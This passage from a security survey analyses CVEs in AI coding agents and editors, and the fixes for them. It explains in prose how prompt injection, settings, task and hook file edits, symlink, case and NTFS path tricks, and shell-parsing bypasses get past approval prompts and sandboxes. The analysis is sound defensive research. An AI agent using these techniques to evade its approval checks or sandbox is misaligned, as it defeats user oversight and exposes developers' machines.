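MITRE published the public record much later, on April 14, 2026, and it probably gives the wrong range of vulnerable versions. It lists "v0.23.0 and before" as vulnerable (GCVE, 2026), but Mill and Vanunu tested the fix in 0.23.0 and found that it worked. Their article is the record's only reference, so their version number is the better evidence. A security scanner that uses the record could still flag 0.23.0 as unsafe.

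Amazon Q's extension for VS Code trusted a project's MCP settings in the same way as Codex. Wiz's *MCP Auto-Execution* describes the flaw, in which the extension loaded MCP servers from the open project and ran their commands without the user's consent. Codex's read-only rule for the `.codex` folder would not have prevented CVE-2025-61260, because the malicious files were in place before the agent started.

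### Comparing the remedies

A vendor can protect a list of named files, ask the user before any change to the agent's settings takes effect, tie each approval to the exact contents that the user approved, or keep the settings outside the workspace. The table shows how well each would have worked against four flaws that became public after August 2025.

| Later flaw | Protect named files | Ask before a change takes effect | Tie approval to contents | Keep settings outside the workspace |
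|---|---|---|---|---|
| Copilot, CVE-2025-62222: the agent creates a settings file | Only if the guard covers new files | Partly | Partly | Partly |
| Cursor, CVE-2025-59944: a change of letter case disguises the MCP file | Only if the guard ignores letter case | Yes | In principle | Only if the agent cannot write there |
| Kiro, CVE-2026-10591: the agent writes an editor task | Only if the list includes the file | No | No | No |
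| Kiro, July 2026: the agent rewrites the MCP file in the home folder | Only if the list includes the file | Yes | Yes | No |

**Protecting named files** is the most direct remedy, and it covers everything in a file, including settings unrelated to AI. It would have stopped Rehberger's original attack on Copilot. However, the vendor must think of every file and every way of reaching it. CVE-2026-25725 was a similar gap in Claude Code's sandbox, involving a settings file that did not exist yet.

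The list also has to include files that belong to other products. Embrace The Red points out that developers often use several agents in one project, so a hijacked agent could rewrite another agent's allowlist or add a server to that agent's MCP settings. Terminal commands can also change files without using the agent's editing tool. VS Code tries to detect when a command will write to a file, but Microsoft's *Manage approvals and permissions* warns that detection is limited and obfuscated commands can evade it.

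**Asking the user before a change takes effect** works without recognising the file's name. The program compares the settings it is about to use with those it used before, so it doesn't matter who changed the file or how they wrote its path. This would have stopped CurXecute and the MCP attack on Amp. It would also have stopped the Codex flaw if Codex had treated the project's settings as new.

Copilot's entry in the table is "partly" because `.vscode/settings.json` holds ordinary editor settings as well as the agent's. The remedy also depends on the user reading the question. VS Code shows its warning about global auto-approve only the first time someone enables the option, so the warning may not protect a person who accepted it long ago and has since turned the option off.

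**Tying approval to contents** is the narrowest remedy and the one that fixed MCPoison. It would have caught the rewritten server entry in Kiro. But it covers only the text the user approved. If an approved entry runs a script stored in the project, an attacker can change the script without changing the entry.

Cursor began requiring a new approval for every changed MCP entry in version 1.3, yet Geordie AI's *Technical Advisory* lists versions up to 1.6.23 as open to remote code execution through CVE-2025-59944. Either the check did not cover every MCP file, or attackers could use another protected file instead.

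**Keeping settings outside the workspace** stops a project from supplying its own rules. It would have prevented MCPoison, the Codex flaw, and Rehberger's attack on Copilot. Rehberger recommended it to AWS for Kiro's allowlist. But Amp's settings and the Kiro file that Intezer's attack changed were already outside the project, so the remedy works only if the agent also cannot write to the new location.

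Keeping settings out of the project is a drawback for teams that share them that way. Claude Code still reads a settings file from the project, along with the user's own file and one that an organisation can deploy. VS Code has partly moved away from project settings. In its current Copilot sessions on the user's own machine, it syncs saved approvals for terminal commands and web addresses with the user's settings and does not copy them from the workspace.

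According to GitHub, an organisation's administrator can also turn off global auto-approve in VS Code so that users cannot turn it back on. A planted edit to the user's settings should then be unable to turn it back on either. None of this would have stopped the Kiro flaw involving `.vscode/tasks.json`, because that file contains instructions for the editor and can be changed without altering the agent's own settings.

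## How do ordinary editor features turn a file edit into code execution?

The Kiro flaw involving `.vscode/tasks.json` is one of a larger group in which the agent makes a permitted edit and an older editor feature causes the harm. Editors constantly act on files in the project folder, such as by downloading reference files, looking for programming languages installed on the machine and running checks in the background. Most of these features predate coding agents, and their designers expected a person to write the files.

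In December 2025, security researcher Ari Marzouk (also spelled Marzuk) published the best-known study of these flaws under the name IDEsaster. An IDE, or integrated development environment, is a code editor with built-in tools for building and testing programs. Over six months, Marzouk found more than 30 flaws, of which 24 received CVE numbers, according to The Hacker News. Maloyan and Namiot report more than 30 CVEs, but they appear to have confused the two counts.

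An IDEsaster attack has three steps. Planted text first takes control of the model. The agent then uses tools that need no approval, usually to edit a file in the workspace. Finally, the editor reacts to the edit by contacting a web address or running a program. Rehberger's attack on Copilot used an edit to change what the agent could do, but an IDEsaster attack can work without changing the agent's permissions or having it request a terminal command.

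All ten products that Marzouk tested were affected, according to Tom's Hardware's *Critical flaws found in AI development tools are dubbed an 'IDEsaster'*: GitHub Copilot, Cursor, Windsurf, Kiro, Zed, Roo Code, Junie, Cline, Gemini CLI and Claude Code. The last two run in a terminal, but they can change files that the developer also has open in an editor. "Affected" therefore means that a hijacked agent could use an editor's features to do harm, not that every attack worked in every product or that the vendor accepted the result as a vulnerability. Anthropic responded to two of the attacks with a security warning for Claude Code.

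### A JSON file that makes the editor fetch a web address

Many programs store their settings in JSON, a text format. A JSON file can include the web address of a schema, a separate file that lists the fields the JSON file may contain. The editor downloads the schema so it can suggest field names, explain them and mark mistakes.

To exploit this, a hijacked agent reads something private, such as a file of access keys, and writes a JSON file whose schema address points to the attacker's server and contains the private data. When the editor requests the schema, it sends the data to the attacker. The agent doesn't need permission to use the network, because the editor makes the request.

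In Marzouk's tests, the request went out even when the product showed a preview of the changes, probably because the changed file was already on disk, as in VS Code.

In Cursor, this flaw is CVE-2025-49150. According to *CVE-2025-49150* (2025), a record kept by Spain's national cybersecurity institute, INCIBE, Cursor downloaded schemas by default without asking for confirmation. Version 0.51.0 turned the downloads off by default. The flaw's severity score is 5.9 (medium), lower than for most flaws of this kind, because the attack leaks data but runs no code. The record also treats the attack as starting after a prompt injection has succeeded.

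VS Code, Zed and JetBrains editors all fetched schemas the same way. Roo Code, an agent that runs as a VS Code extension, and Junie, JetBrains' agent, each received a CVE for the flaw. Copilot and Kiro were also affected but received no CVE.

### A setting that names a program to run

The second attack does run code. Some editor settings hold the path to a program that the editor starts when needed. In VS Code, `php.validate.executablePath` holds the path to the program that checks PHP files for errors.

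The hijacked agent writes the attacker's code into an executable file already in the workspace, then changes the setting to point to that file. The editor runs the code as soon as a PHP file opens or the agent creates one. The attack probably reuses an existing file because file-editing tools usually can't mark a new one as executable. JetBrains editors have a similar weakness in `.idea/workspace.xml`, where a setting can specify the path to Git.

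Like CurXecute, Cursor's version of this flaw, CVE-2025-54130, arose because the agent could create a dotfile without approval. If a project had no `.vscode/settings.json`, the agent could add a malicious one, according to NVD's *CVE-2025-54130 Detail* (2025). Cursor fixed the flaw in version 1.3.9.

The Hacker News lists the Copilot version of this attack under CVE-2025-53773, the number Microsoft gave to Rehberger's auto-approve attack. One unapproved edit to the settings file could enable either attack. Fixing only the auto-approve option would have left attackers able to use the PHP setting, or any other setting that names a program.

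### Settings for several folders at once

VS Code can open several folders together as a multi-root workspace. It lists the folders in a `.code-workspace` file, which can also hold editor settings. A hijacked agent can therefore put the same dangerous setting in that file, even if `.vscode/settings.json` is protected.

NVD's *CVE-2025-61590 Detail* describes an attack that uses a workspace file to bypass Cursor's fix for CVE-2025-54130, affecting versions up to 1.6. The agent needs a workspace file it can reach, but the user doesn't have to have saved one because VS Code creates an untitled one automatically. Cursor fixed the flaw in version 1.7. The NVD record, published two months after the one for CVE-2025-54130, does not describe the fix.

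Microsoft's equivalent is CVE-2025-64660, fixed in VS Code 1.106.2 on November 20, 2025. Microsoft's *MSRC_CVE-2025-64660* (2025) credits Marzouk, Tarek Nakkouch and AmeenBasha M K, and scores the flaw 8.0. Five days after publishing the advisory, Microsoft updated the score and corrected the stated impact to remote code execution.

The published accounts differ on how much the victim has to do. The Hacker News reported that attacks through settings and workspace files need no user interaction, because the products approve edits inside the workspace by default. According to Microsoft's record, the user must trust the malicious file and then ask Copilot for help. Copilot users routinely ask for help, so that condition offers little protection. Trusting the file is a deliberate choice in VS Code, but less so in Cursor, where workspace trust is off by default.

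The table shows where The Hacker News places the three attacks. A dash means only that the article does not list the combination.

| Product | Schema address | Setting that names a program | Multi-root workspace |
|---|---|---|---|
| Cursor | CVE-2025-49150 | CVE-2025-54130 | CVE-2025-61590 |
| GitHub Copilot | No CVE | CVE-2025-53773 | CVE-2025-64660 |
| Roo Code | CVE-2025-53097 | CVE-2025-53536 | CVE-2025-58372 |
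| Junie (JetBrains) | CVE-2025-58335 | – | – |
| Zed | – | CVE-2025-55012 | – |
| Kiro | No CVE | – | – |
| Claude Code | Security warning | Security warning | – |

The ten CVEs in the table use only three techniques, so IDEsaster's totals are a better guide to how many products share a weakness than to how many different weaknesses exist.

### Three cases where the agent was in a sandbox

In July 2026 Pillar Security published a series of attacks on sandboxed agents. *The Week of Sandbox Escapes* (Cohen, Lisichkin and Fogel, 2026) describes the common problem as programs outside the sandbox reading and acting on files the agent can write. Three of the attacks use the same pattern as IDEsaster.

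**Python's interpreter in Cursor.** A Python project often has a virtual environment, a folder containing the project's libraries and a copy of, or link to, the interpreter that runs its code. Cursor comes with Microsoft's Python extension, which runs outside the sandbox. The extension searches a newly opened workspace for virtual environments and runs each one's interpreter to find out its version.

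*The Week of Sandbox Escapes Day 3* (Lisichkin, 2026) showed that a sandboxed agent could replace the interpreter with a script. The script ran the attacker's command and then started the real interpreter, so the extension still got the expected response. If the project had no virtual environment, the agent could create one, which also triggered the search without a restart.

The extension recognises an environment by the files inside it, up to two levels below the top of the workspace, so stopping the agent from writing to folders with the usual names, such as `.venv`, would not be enough. Lisichkin got the same result with folders called `data_cache` and `build_output`, and recommended either turning off the automatic search or stopping the sandboxed agent from writing the files that make up an environment.

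The CVE was still pending when Pillar published the attack. NVD's *CVE-2026-73217 Detail* (2026), dated August 11, closely matches the attack. The record covers Cursor on macOS before version 3.1.2, with a score of 7.7. It leaves unclear which of the two remedies, if either, Cursor chose.

Google's Antigravity uses the VS Code codebase and inherited its tasks, which are saved commands that can run when a folder opens. Antigravity's file-writing tools could not write outside the workspace, to `.git`, or to several sensitive names inside `.vscode`. *The Week of Sandbox Escapes Day 7* (Lisichkin, 2026) describes an attack that works because the task file, `tasks.json`, was missing from the list of blocked names.

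In Antigravity, a hijacked agent could write a task and change the setting that controls whether tasks start automatically. The task started only when the user reopened the project, so the planted text instructed the agent to finish by asking the user to restart the editor. The editor's task runner then ran the command outside the sandbox. Google accepted the report but downgraded it, and Cohen and colleagues list no patched version.

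Lisichkin argues that adding `tasks.json` to the list would stop this attack but not others like it. An allowlist of paths the agent may write to would be safer but would interrupt more ordinary work. Lisichkin prefers that the editor not automatically run configuration that an agent wrote.

**A hook file in Cursor.** A hook is a command that a coding agent's software runs at a set moment, such as when the agent finishes its turn. Claude Code can read hooks from files in a project's `.claude` folder, and Cursor added support for the same files. In *The Week of Sandbox Escapes*, Cohen (2026) found that a sandboxed agent in Cursor could write a hook to `.claude/settings.local.json`. Cursor then ran the command outside the sandbox at the end of the turn, without asking the user.

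Cursor fixed this flaw, CVE-2026-48124, in version 3.0.0. NVD's *CVE-2026-48124 Detail* (2026) gives it a score of 8.5. The record also covers a malicious project that already contains the hook file, so the attacker doesn't need to mislead the model.

Cohen attributes the problem to developers treating compatibility features as harmless additions. Developers may protect their own product's settings folder but forget that the product also applies settings from another product's folder. Cohen recommends showing an approval prompt that names the command and the file it came from or, better, running hooks under the same sandbox and rules as the agent's other commands.

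### Is this a new class of vulnerability?

Marzouk presents IDEsaster as a new class of vulnerability, arguing that vendors checked the agent and its tools but left the underlying editor out of their threat model, treating its features as safe "because they've been there for years". Earlier attacks relied on a faulty tool or changed the agent's configuration. In IDEsaster, the tool and the editor feature can both work as designed but be dangerous in combination. In *Exploiting AI IDEs*, a Resilient Cyber podcast interview, Marzouk says other software built before agents, such as cloud systems and collaboration tools, probably has the same gap.

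Editor settings could run code long before agents arrived. SafeDep's *Config Files That Run Code* describes how the Miasma worm, self-spreading malware, placed the same malicious program in seven kinds of configuration file. Some were for AI tools, and others were for VS Code and package managers such as npm. A developer could set off the attack by opening a folder or installing a project's dependencies, without any prompt injection.

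VS Code already had a defence against this danger. *Are AI-assisted Development Tools Immune to Prompt Injection?* (2026) notes that workspace trust restricts automatic tasks in untrusted projects. The public records also classify the flaws under existing CWE types, including code injection, improper authorization and information disclosure. On this view, IDEsaster uses prompt injection to exploit a known editor risk.

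Workspace trust, the older defence, fails here because the developer decides whether to trust a folder when opening it, and a hijacked agent changes the folder afterwards. The developer may have been right to trust the project, and the attacker may have had no access to it except through a web page or an issue that the agent read. Before agents, the attacker had to get a malicious file into the project by some other route, but now the agent can write it.

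Workspace trust can also fail more simply, when an editor lets a project run commands before the trust check. Mascellino (2026) reported in August that Cursor had fixed a flaw of this kind.

The hook case also fits Marzouk's explanation poorly, because hooks for coding agents are recent. A feature's age therefore matters less than whether it runs something from a file the agent can write. IDEsaster is better understood as a new way to reach known weaknesses than as a new type of weakness in the CWE sense. It still needs a different fix, because the editor would have to track who wrote a file as well as whether the user trusts the folder. Cohen and colleagues recommend recording which files came from the user, the project and the agent.

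Developers' complaints give some support to looking beyond the model for the cause of security problems. *Impossible to hide secret* (Akhond, Al Mamun and colleagues, 2026) studied 446 Reddit posts about security and privacy problems in AI coding tools and traced most of the problems to the design of the surrounding system, such as what data it could access and which actions it took unchecked. But the posts mostly describe everyday experience rather than tested attacks, so they can't settle whether IDEsaster is a separate class of vulnerability.

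### Why the flaws spread and the features stay

Cursor, Windsurf, Kiro and Antigravity inherit VS Code's settings, tasks and workspace files, and each vendor has to work out which ones an agent should not edit. AWS and Google both let their agents edit `tasks.json`, and the two cases became public a month apart. An attacker who learns how one of these editors handles a file can try the same approach on the others. Agents that run as extensions, such as Roo Code, depend on the same features but do not control the editor.

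Shared code explains only some of these cases. JetBrains and Zed have their own codebases, but both fetched JSON schemas automatically because developers expect the same conveniences from any editor. Cursor's hook flaw came from supporting another product's file format.

Fixes spread between editors less reliably than flaws do. VS Code has a setting that limits schema downloads to trusted domains, which blocks an attacker's server without disabling the feature. Cursor had not adopted this setting when a user complained on the company's forum, in *Lack of JSON support due to CVE-2025-49150*. With downloads off, Cursor no longer offered suggestions, explanations or checks based on remote schemas, even for basic files such as `package.json`.

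A member of the Cursor team replied that the only way to restore them was to turn downloads back on and accept the risk, preferably only in trusted projects. The user pointed out that a hijacked agent in one of those projects could still read private files elsewhere on the machine, and the team member agreed. There was no date for adding the list of trusted domains. The user called the decision to turn downloads off "correct and responsible" but found working without them "truly horrible".

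The exchange shows that users who need a removed feature will turn it on again, and may then be as exposed as before. The per-project workaround adds another risk because it stores the setting in `.vscode/settings.json`. A malicious project could include that file with downloads already enabled, unless the editor ignored the setting until the user trusted the folder.

Removing the other features would be even more disruptive. An editor that couldn't run a project's Python interpreter would be of little use to a Python developer, and teams rely on tasks and hooks to automate their work. Vendors can instead restrict what starts without the user's approval, or run the helper programs inside the sandbox as well.

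Marzouk's main advice to users is to run the whole setup in a container or virtual machine, isolated from the rest of the computer. That would limit what a replaced Python interpreter could reach, provided the editor's extensions ran inside too. A schema request could still send out data that the agent could read there, unless the isolated environment also restricted network access.

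## Why do checks on file paths fail?

The software can protect a settings file only if it can tell which file a request would touch. The model supplies a path, such as the text `src/app.py`, and the software must use it to decide whether the file is inside the workspace and whether access needs approval. Deny rules, which users write to forbid the agent from opening particular files, depend on the same kind of check.

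Different paths can lead to the same file or folder. Two dots mean "the folder above", so `shop/src/../notes.txt` and `shop/notes.txt` are the same file. A symlink points to another file or folder, but the text of its path doesn't show this. If `shop/readme.txt` is a symlink to a password file in the home folder, a program that opens it gets the password file. Comparing the text of two paths therefore doesn't show whether they lead to the same place.

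A safe check has three steps:

1. Resolve the path. The software follows every dot and symlink to find the real location, known as the canonical path.
2. Compare that location with the boundary, one whole folder name at a time. The boundary must be a resolved location too.
3. Open the file that passed the check, without looking up the path again.

### The edge of the workspace

In CVE-2025-54794, Claude Code checked only whether a requested path began with the workspace's path. If a developer worked in `/home/ana/shop` and kept customer records in `/home/ana/shop-private`, Claude Code would have treated `/home/ana/shop-private/customers.csv` as part of the workspace, because its path also begins with `/home/ana/shop`. The agent could then have read the file without asking.

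*InversePrompt* describes how Beber found the flaw by unpacking Claude Code's compressed program with Claude's help. Beber had already found the same error in Anthropic's Filesystem MCP Server and looked for it in Claude Code first. Claude Code resolved the "." and ".." segments in both paths before comparing them, but it didn't check that the matching text ended at a folder boundary.

According to MITRE's *Claude Code Research Preview has a Path Restriction Bypass* (2025), the attacker needed to plant text for the model to read and find or create a folder with a suitable name. These requirements limit the attack, but developers do keep folders like `shop-old` beside the original. Beber adds that a symlink in the neighbouring folder could extend access to any part of the disk.

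Windsurf had a more basic problem. HiddenLayer's *Path Traversal in File Tools Allowing Arbitrary Filesystem Access* (2025) describes a test in which a README falsely described the whole `C:` drive as the user's workspace. The agent then read a file elsewhere on the drive and overwrote it. The attack worked even with automatic execution off and the file-writing tool on the deny list.

HiddenLayer wrote that the planted text changed the workspace path. If so, no other part of the program was enforcing the boundary. An editor already records which folder the user opened, so text in a README should not affect where the workspace ends.

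The Windsurf flaw is CVE-2025-62353. GCVE's *CVE-2025-62353* (2025) matches HiddenLayer's description and has the same publication date, but it lists all versions as affected, while HiddenLayer lists 1.12.12 and older. OpenCVE's *CVE-2025-62353* (2025) lists no vendor fix or workaround, so it is safer to assume that all versions are affected.

### One file, many spellings

Ashkenazi and Tsukerman's Black Hat talk included a function that decides whether a file is sensitive by comparing the end of its path with the names of Cursor's MCP settings file and two VS Code files. Any other spelling of those names gets past such a function, even if the operating system opens the same file.

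The simplest way to get past a path check is to change the path's letter case. Windows and macOS normally ignore case in file names, so `.cursor/mcp.json` and `.Cursor/mcp.json` refer to the same file. Brett Gustafson of the security company Lakera found that Cursor checked only for the exact lower-case name. When the agent used a capital letter, Cursor treated the path as a new, unprotected file and skipped the approval prompt. The operating system then wrote to the real MCP settings file. MITRE's *Cursor IDE* (2025) records this vulnerability as CVE-2025-59944.

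Cursor's command-line agent had the same flaw in the check that protects its settings. MITRE published the flaw as CVE-2025-61593 in *Cursor CLI Agent* (2025) on October 3, the same day as the editor's flaw. The developers had written a fix but not yet released it.

A month later, Cursor disclosed two more problems with how paths are spelled, both on Windows. According to CVELogic's *Cursor is Vulnerable to Path Manipulation Using Backslashes on Windows* (2025), the editor already caught paths padded with extra dots and forward slashes but missed those padded with dots and backslashes, which Windows also accepts. The other problem, described in MITRE's *Cursor's Sensitive File Modification can Lead to NTFS Path Quirks* (2025), came from NTFS, the usual Windows file system.

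NTFS can give a file with a long name a second, shorter name for compatibility with old DOS programs. A folder called `.agent` may also have the name `AGENT~1`. NTFS divides files into streams of data, and a path that names a file's main stream leads to its ordinary contents. Ashkenazi and Tsukerman demonstrated both kinds of alternative name, though MITRE's record doesn't specify which ones worked in Cursor.

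Ignoring letter case is a reasonable fix for a list of protected files, because the worst result is that the user is asked an unnecessary question on Linux, where case usually matters. The same change would be a mistake in a workspace check on Linux, because `Shop` and `shop` can be different folders and the agent may have permission to use only one of them.

### Symlinks that get past the rules

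A deny rule does little to protect a file if the agent can reach it under another name. According to MITRE's record of CVE-2025-59829, Claude Code did not account for symlinks when it applied deny rules, so the agent could access a denied file by opening a link to it. Anthropic fixed the flaw, then disclosed a nearly identical one, CVE-2026-25724, four months later.

Terra Security's *When AI Becomes the Attack Surface* explains how the company found the later flaw. A researcher denied Claude Code access to a file, created a symlink to it named `test.py`, and found that the agent read the file through the symlink. Git can store symlinks, so a downloaded project may already contain one. A comment about a known bug in `test.py` could be enough to make the agent open it during an ordinary code review.

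MITRE's *Claude Code Has Permission Deny Bypass Through Symbolic Links* (2026) does not explain why the problem came back. The first fix may have missed a way around the check, or a later change may have reintroduced the flaw. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-32018* (2025) describes an example of the second cause, a Cursor update that accidentally let the agent write outside the workspace. It calls that flaw highly impractical to exploit because it required deliberate prompting, and says the user was unlikely to miss the edit, which Cursor still showed for review.

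Software that resolves symlinks can still fail when an agent is about to create a file. The usual function for resolving a path returns an error if nothing exists there, and Ashkenazi and Tsukerman found that most agents responded by using the original, unresolved path. If a folder in that path links to a location outside the workspace, the path still appears to be inside the workspace, and the attacker can create a file outside it.

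Cursor made this mistake. According to MITRE's *CVE-2026-50549*, a hijacked agent could cause the error by linking to a file that didn't exist or by removing read permission from the path, and Cursor would then write through the link without approval. A safer program would resolve the nearest existing folder, add the new file's name, check that the resulting path isn't a link, and refuse the request after any other error.

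### What the approval prompt shows

The approval prompt also needs to show the user the resolved path, or it may name the wrong file. Wiz's *GhostApproval* describes tests of six agents on a project where `project_settings.json` was a link to a sensitive file in the user's home folder. Claude Code, Cursor and Antigravity showed the link's name when they asked for approval. In Claude Code, the model's reasoning had identified the file as a shell configuration file, but the prompt didn't include this.

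The other three agents gave the user even less control. Amazon Q and Windsurf changed the file before offering a chance to undo or reject the edit, and Augment changed it without asking. AWS, Google and Cursor had fixed their products by the time Wiz published in July 2026. Wiz listed the fixes for Augment and Windsurf as in progress.

It is unclear when Claude Code's prompts became accurate. Anthropic told Wiz that the file-editing dialog had warned about symlinks since version 2.1.32, but Wiz lists the later version 2.1.42 as affected. In *SymJack*, Utevsky (2026) found no warning for some shell copies in version 2.1.128 and a partial improvement in 2.1.129, which warned about a project's MCP file but still named the link instead of the file it pointed to.

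In November, *클로드 코드 VS코드 확장, 승인 창에 심볼릭 링크 목적지 안 보여줘* (송, 2026) reported a researcher's claim that Claude Code's VS Code extension still hid a symbolic link's destination in the approval prompt in version 2.1.322, although Anthropic had improved the terminal version. File edits, shell commands and the extension apparently use different code to show their prompts, so fixing one doesn't necessarily fix the others.

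### Routes that the check does not cover

When a user allowed Claude Code to edit files, that permission also covered shell commands that move and copy files within the workspace. Ashkenazi and Tsukerman found that Claude Code blocked a command that moved a file directly onto `.claude/settings.json`, but that the agent could rename the `.claude` folder, edit the settings file inside it, and restore the folder's name.

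Resolving the path would not have stopped this, because the file was in an unprotected place when the agent edited it. The software would also have to ask the user for approval before the agent renames any folder that contains a protected file, or moves another folder into its place.

Claude Code also missed move commands that gave the destination folder as an option. On Windows, backslashes again got past the check. Variables and wildcards, which the shell replaces with real names only when it runs the command, also got past it.

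Utevsky combined a copy command with a symlink. A malicious project contained a link that looked like a video file but pointed to the agent's settings. The project also included instructions to copy another "video" onto that link. The approval prompt showed the command as written, so the user saw a request to copy a video into a documentation folder. The attack worked against command-line agents from Anthropic, Google, Cursor, GitHub and xAI.

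Utevsky traces the flaw to several checks that each use a different description of the same write. The file-editing tool uses a list of sensitive paths and the shell prompt shows the command's text, but neither includes the link's destination. Utevsky therefore recommends that agents apply the same rules to shell copies as to other file writes.

The same gap affects file reads. In September 2026, HiddenLayer disclosed that Mistral Vibe, another coding agent, automatically approved 31 commands without checking their paths, which gave the agent access to files anywhere on the machine (CVE-2026-87988).

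### Between the check and the write

Even a correct check can be out of date by the time the program acts on it. If the program checks a path and then opens the file by name, the operating system looks up the path a second time, and another program may have changed what is there since the check. Security researchers call this a time-of-check to time-of-use (TOCTOU) flaw.

In the version that Ashkenazi and Tsukerman describe, a command the agent has already started repeatedly swaps an ordinary file and a symlink at the same path. The check may eventually happen while the ordinary file is there and the write while the symlink is there, so the data is written wherever the symlink points. The code in their example was vulnerable because it resolved the path to a string, which the program then had to look up again.

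A program can make sure it writes to the same file it checked by using a handle, a reference to an open file that the operating system provides. The handle still refers to that file even if someone renames it or puts another in its place. The program can open the file without changing it, check which file it has, and write through the same handle only if that file is allowed.

Linux and macOS offer an option called `O_NOFOLLOW`, which makes opening a file fail if the last part of the path is a symlink. The system still follows symlinks in the folders before that. Linux's `openat2` call can cover the whole path. The program supplies a handle to the workspace folder and the option `RESOLVE_BENEATH`, and Linux refuses any path that leads outside that folder. The check and the opening happen in one operation, so an attacker can't change the path between them.

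`RESOLVE_BENEATH` doesn't check whether a file inside the workspace is a protected settings file. The program can check this by comparing the identifying numbers that the file system gives existing files, since a file's number stays the same however its path is spelled. A file that doesn't exist yet has no such number, so the program has to identify the parent folder and compare the new name with the protected file's name under that file system's rules.

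Claude Code's CVE-2026-46406 involved a similar weakness, but the attacker didn't have to win a race. The `/copy` command saved the model's response to `/tmp/claude/response.md`, a fixed location in a folder shared by everyone with an account on the computer. Another user could create the `claude` folder first and put a symlink named `response.md` in it. When a more privileged user ran `/copy`, Claude Code followed the link and overwrote a file of the attacker's choice with the response.

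Claude Code also let every user on the computer read the same file, so it could leak information even without a symlink. MITRE's record lists separation between users, an unpredictable name and a defence against symlinks as missing. Programs normally avoid the problem by creating temporary files in a private folder and telling the operating system to return an error if something already exists at the path.

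### Which fixes reached the cause?

Vendors seldom publish the code they changed, so later flaws are often the best evidence of how far a fix went.

| Flaw | Fixed in | What the fix dealt with |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code, similar folder names (CVE-2025-54794) | 0.2.111 | The prefix error, but not symlinks in deny rules |
| Cursor, letter case (CVE-2025-59944) | 1.7 | Letter case and some padded paths, but not backslashes |
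| Cursor, backslashes (CVE-2025-64107) | 2.0 | Apparently one kind of spelling |
| Cursor, alternative Windows names (CVE-2025-64108) | 2.0 | Several spellings, by an unpublished method |
| Claude Code, symlinks and deny rules (CVE-2025-59829) | 1.0.120 | Only part of the cause, or a fix that did not last |
| Claude Code, symlinks and deny rules again (CVE-2026-25724) | 2.1.7 | Possibly the cause, by an unpublished method |
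| Cursor, unresolved paths (CVE-2026-50549) | 3.0 | Probably the unsafe response to an error |
| Claude Code, `/copy` (CVE-2026-46406) | 2.1.128 | Unpublished |
| Windsurf, path traversal (CVE-2025-62353) | None listed | – |

Cursor's fixes show that handling a few spellings of a path at a time can leave others unblocked. Lakera reports that version 1.7 normalized paths and ignored letter case when comparing them. But CVELogic lists versions up to 1.7.52 as vulnerable to the backslash trick, so the normalization must have missed backslashes.

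Lakera concludes more broadly that protections should consider an action's purpose as well as the file's name. That could help with the copied "video", where the command looked ordinary but its stated purpose was false. It is a weaker answer to the spelling flaws, because the file system can establish exactly which file a path leads to. Judging purpose would probably rely on another model, which planted text might also mislead.

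## Why do lists of safe commands fail?

A terminal command is harder to judge in advance than a file path. A command may read a file, overwrite one, start another program or contact a server, and the software has to determine which from a line of text. Allowlists usually contain commands that normally only display information, such as `ls`, `echo` and `git status`. An attacker tries to write a line that the software accepts as one of these commands but that does something else.

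### How an agent decides whether to ask

Chen and Lin (2026), in *One Goal, Many Commands*, describe the usual arrangement as three lists. The agent refuses anything on a denylist, which names forbidden commands, and runs anything on the allowlist without asking. Everything else goes to the user or, in some products, to a second model. To apply the lists, the software has to interpret the line:

1. It splits the line into separate commands. For example, `git status && npm test` contains two, and both need permission.
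2. It identifies the program that each command would start. It may also examine the options, which are words such as `--help` that change what a program does.
3. It compares the result with the lists. If every command matches an allowlist entry, the line runs without an approval prompt.

The shell then reads the original line again by its own rules, under which a pair of quotation marks can change what runs. For example, `echo "build; test"` prints some text, while `echo build; test` runs two commands. Adversa AI found that many agents' filters inspect the raw text, although Bash, a common shell, removes quotation marks and fills in variables before it runs anything. The filter and the shell can therefore interpret the same line differently.

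Some products check a command several times. In *An Evening with Claude (Code)*, Chester (2025) took apart version 2.0.25 of Claude Code and found regular expressions (patterns for matching text) that described acceptable forms of common commands, and a separate list of the options each command could take. Claude Code also sent some lines to Haiku, a smaller Anthropic model, which had to name the command at the start or report that the line hid another one. When Chester tried a `git branch` line that matched one of the patterns but had a second command attached, Claude Code still asked for approval.

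### Eight flaws in Claude Code

Between August 2025 and February 2026, Anthropic disclosed eight flaws that let a command get past these checks. Another flaw in the command checks, CVE-2025-55284, let an allowed command leak data.

| Made public | CVE | Where the check failed | Fixed in |
|---|---|---|---|
| August 4, 2025 | CVE-2025-54795 | `echo`, which prints text | 1.0.20 |
| September 10, 2025 | CVE-2025-58764 | `rg`, which searches files | 1.0.105 |
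| November 20, 2025 | CVE-2025-64755 | `sed`, which edits text | 2.0.31 |
| December 3, 2025 | CVE-2025-66032 | Variables and short options | 1.0.93 |
| February 3, 2026 | CVE-2026-24887 | `find`, which looks for files | 2.0.72 |
| February 3, 2026 | CVE-2026-24053 | Zsh syntax for writing to a file | 2.0.74 |
| February 6, 2026 | CVE-2026-25722 | A change of folder before a write | 2.0.57 |
| February 6, 2026 | CVE-2026-25723 | `echo` output sent to `sed` | 2.0.55 |

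The `echo` flaw came from assuming that the shell would treat anything in quotation marks only as text. According to Cymulate's *Frequently Asked Questions*, Beber closed the quoted string early and continued with another command. Claude Code treated the whole line as one `echo` command, but the shell ran the second command too. The GitHub Advisory Database's *Claude Code echo command allowed bypass of user approval prompt* (2025) notes that Anthropic later forced everyone on versions before 1.0.24 to update. By version 2.0.25, the pattern for `echo` no longer accepted stray quotation marks, or line breaks inside a quoted string.

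CVE-2025-66032 covers several mistakes. In *Pwning Claude Code in 8 Different Ways*, RyotaK (2026) noticed Claude Code running a command without approval and found eight ways to make it do so. Two of them used shell variables. One used `$IFS`, which can stand for a space. Claude Code treated a search pattern containing it as one word, but the shell split it into several, including an option that makes `rg` run a program on each file. The other assembled forbidden syntax from several variables, then used a Bash feature that runs commands stored in a variable's value.

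Four more attacks worked because Claude Code relied on blocking a command's dangerous options to make it safe. For `man`, it blocked the usual ways of choosing a program to display a page but missed an option that chooses a program to show the page as HTML. For `sort`, it blocked writing to a file but missed an option that names a compression program to run. The `history` command, which lists earlier commands, could also save the attacker's text to a file that the shell runs at startup. For Git, Claude Code blocked `--upload-pack`, which can name a program to run, but Git accepts shortened option names, so `--upload-pa` still worked.

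Claude Code's check for `xargs`, a program that runs another command on a list of items, treated every option as if it took a value. The `-t` option takes none, so Claude Code read the command to run as the option's value. MITRE's *CVE-2025-66032* (2025) mentions only `$IFS` and short options, so a reader who relies on that record would miss most of RyotaK's findings.

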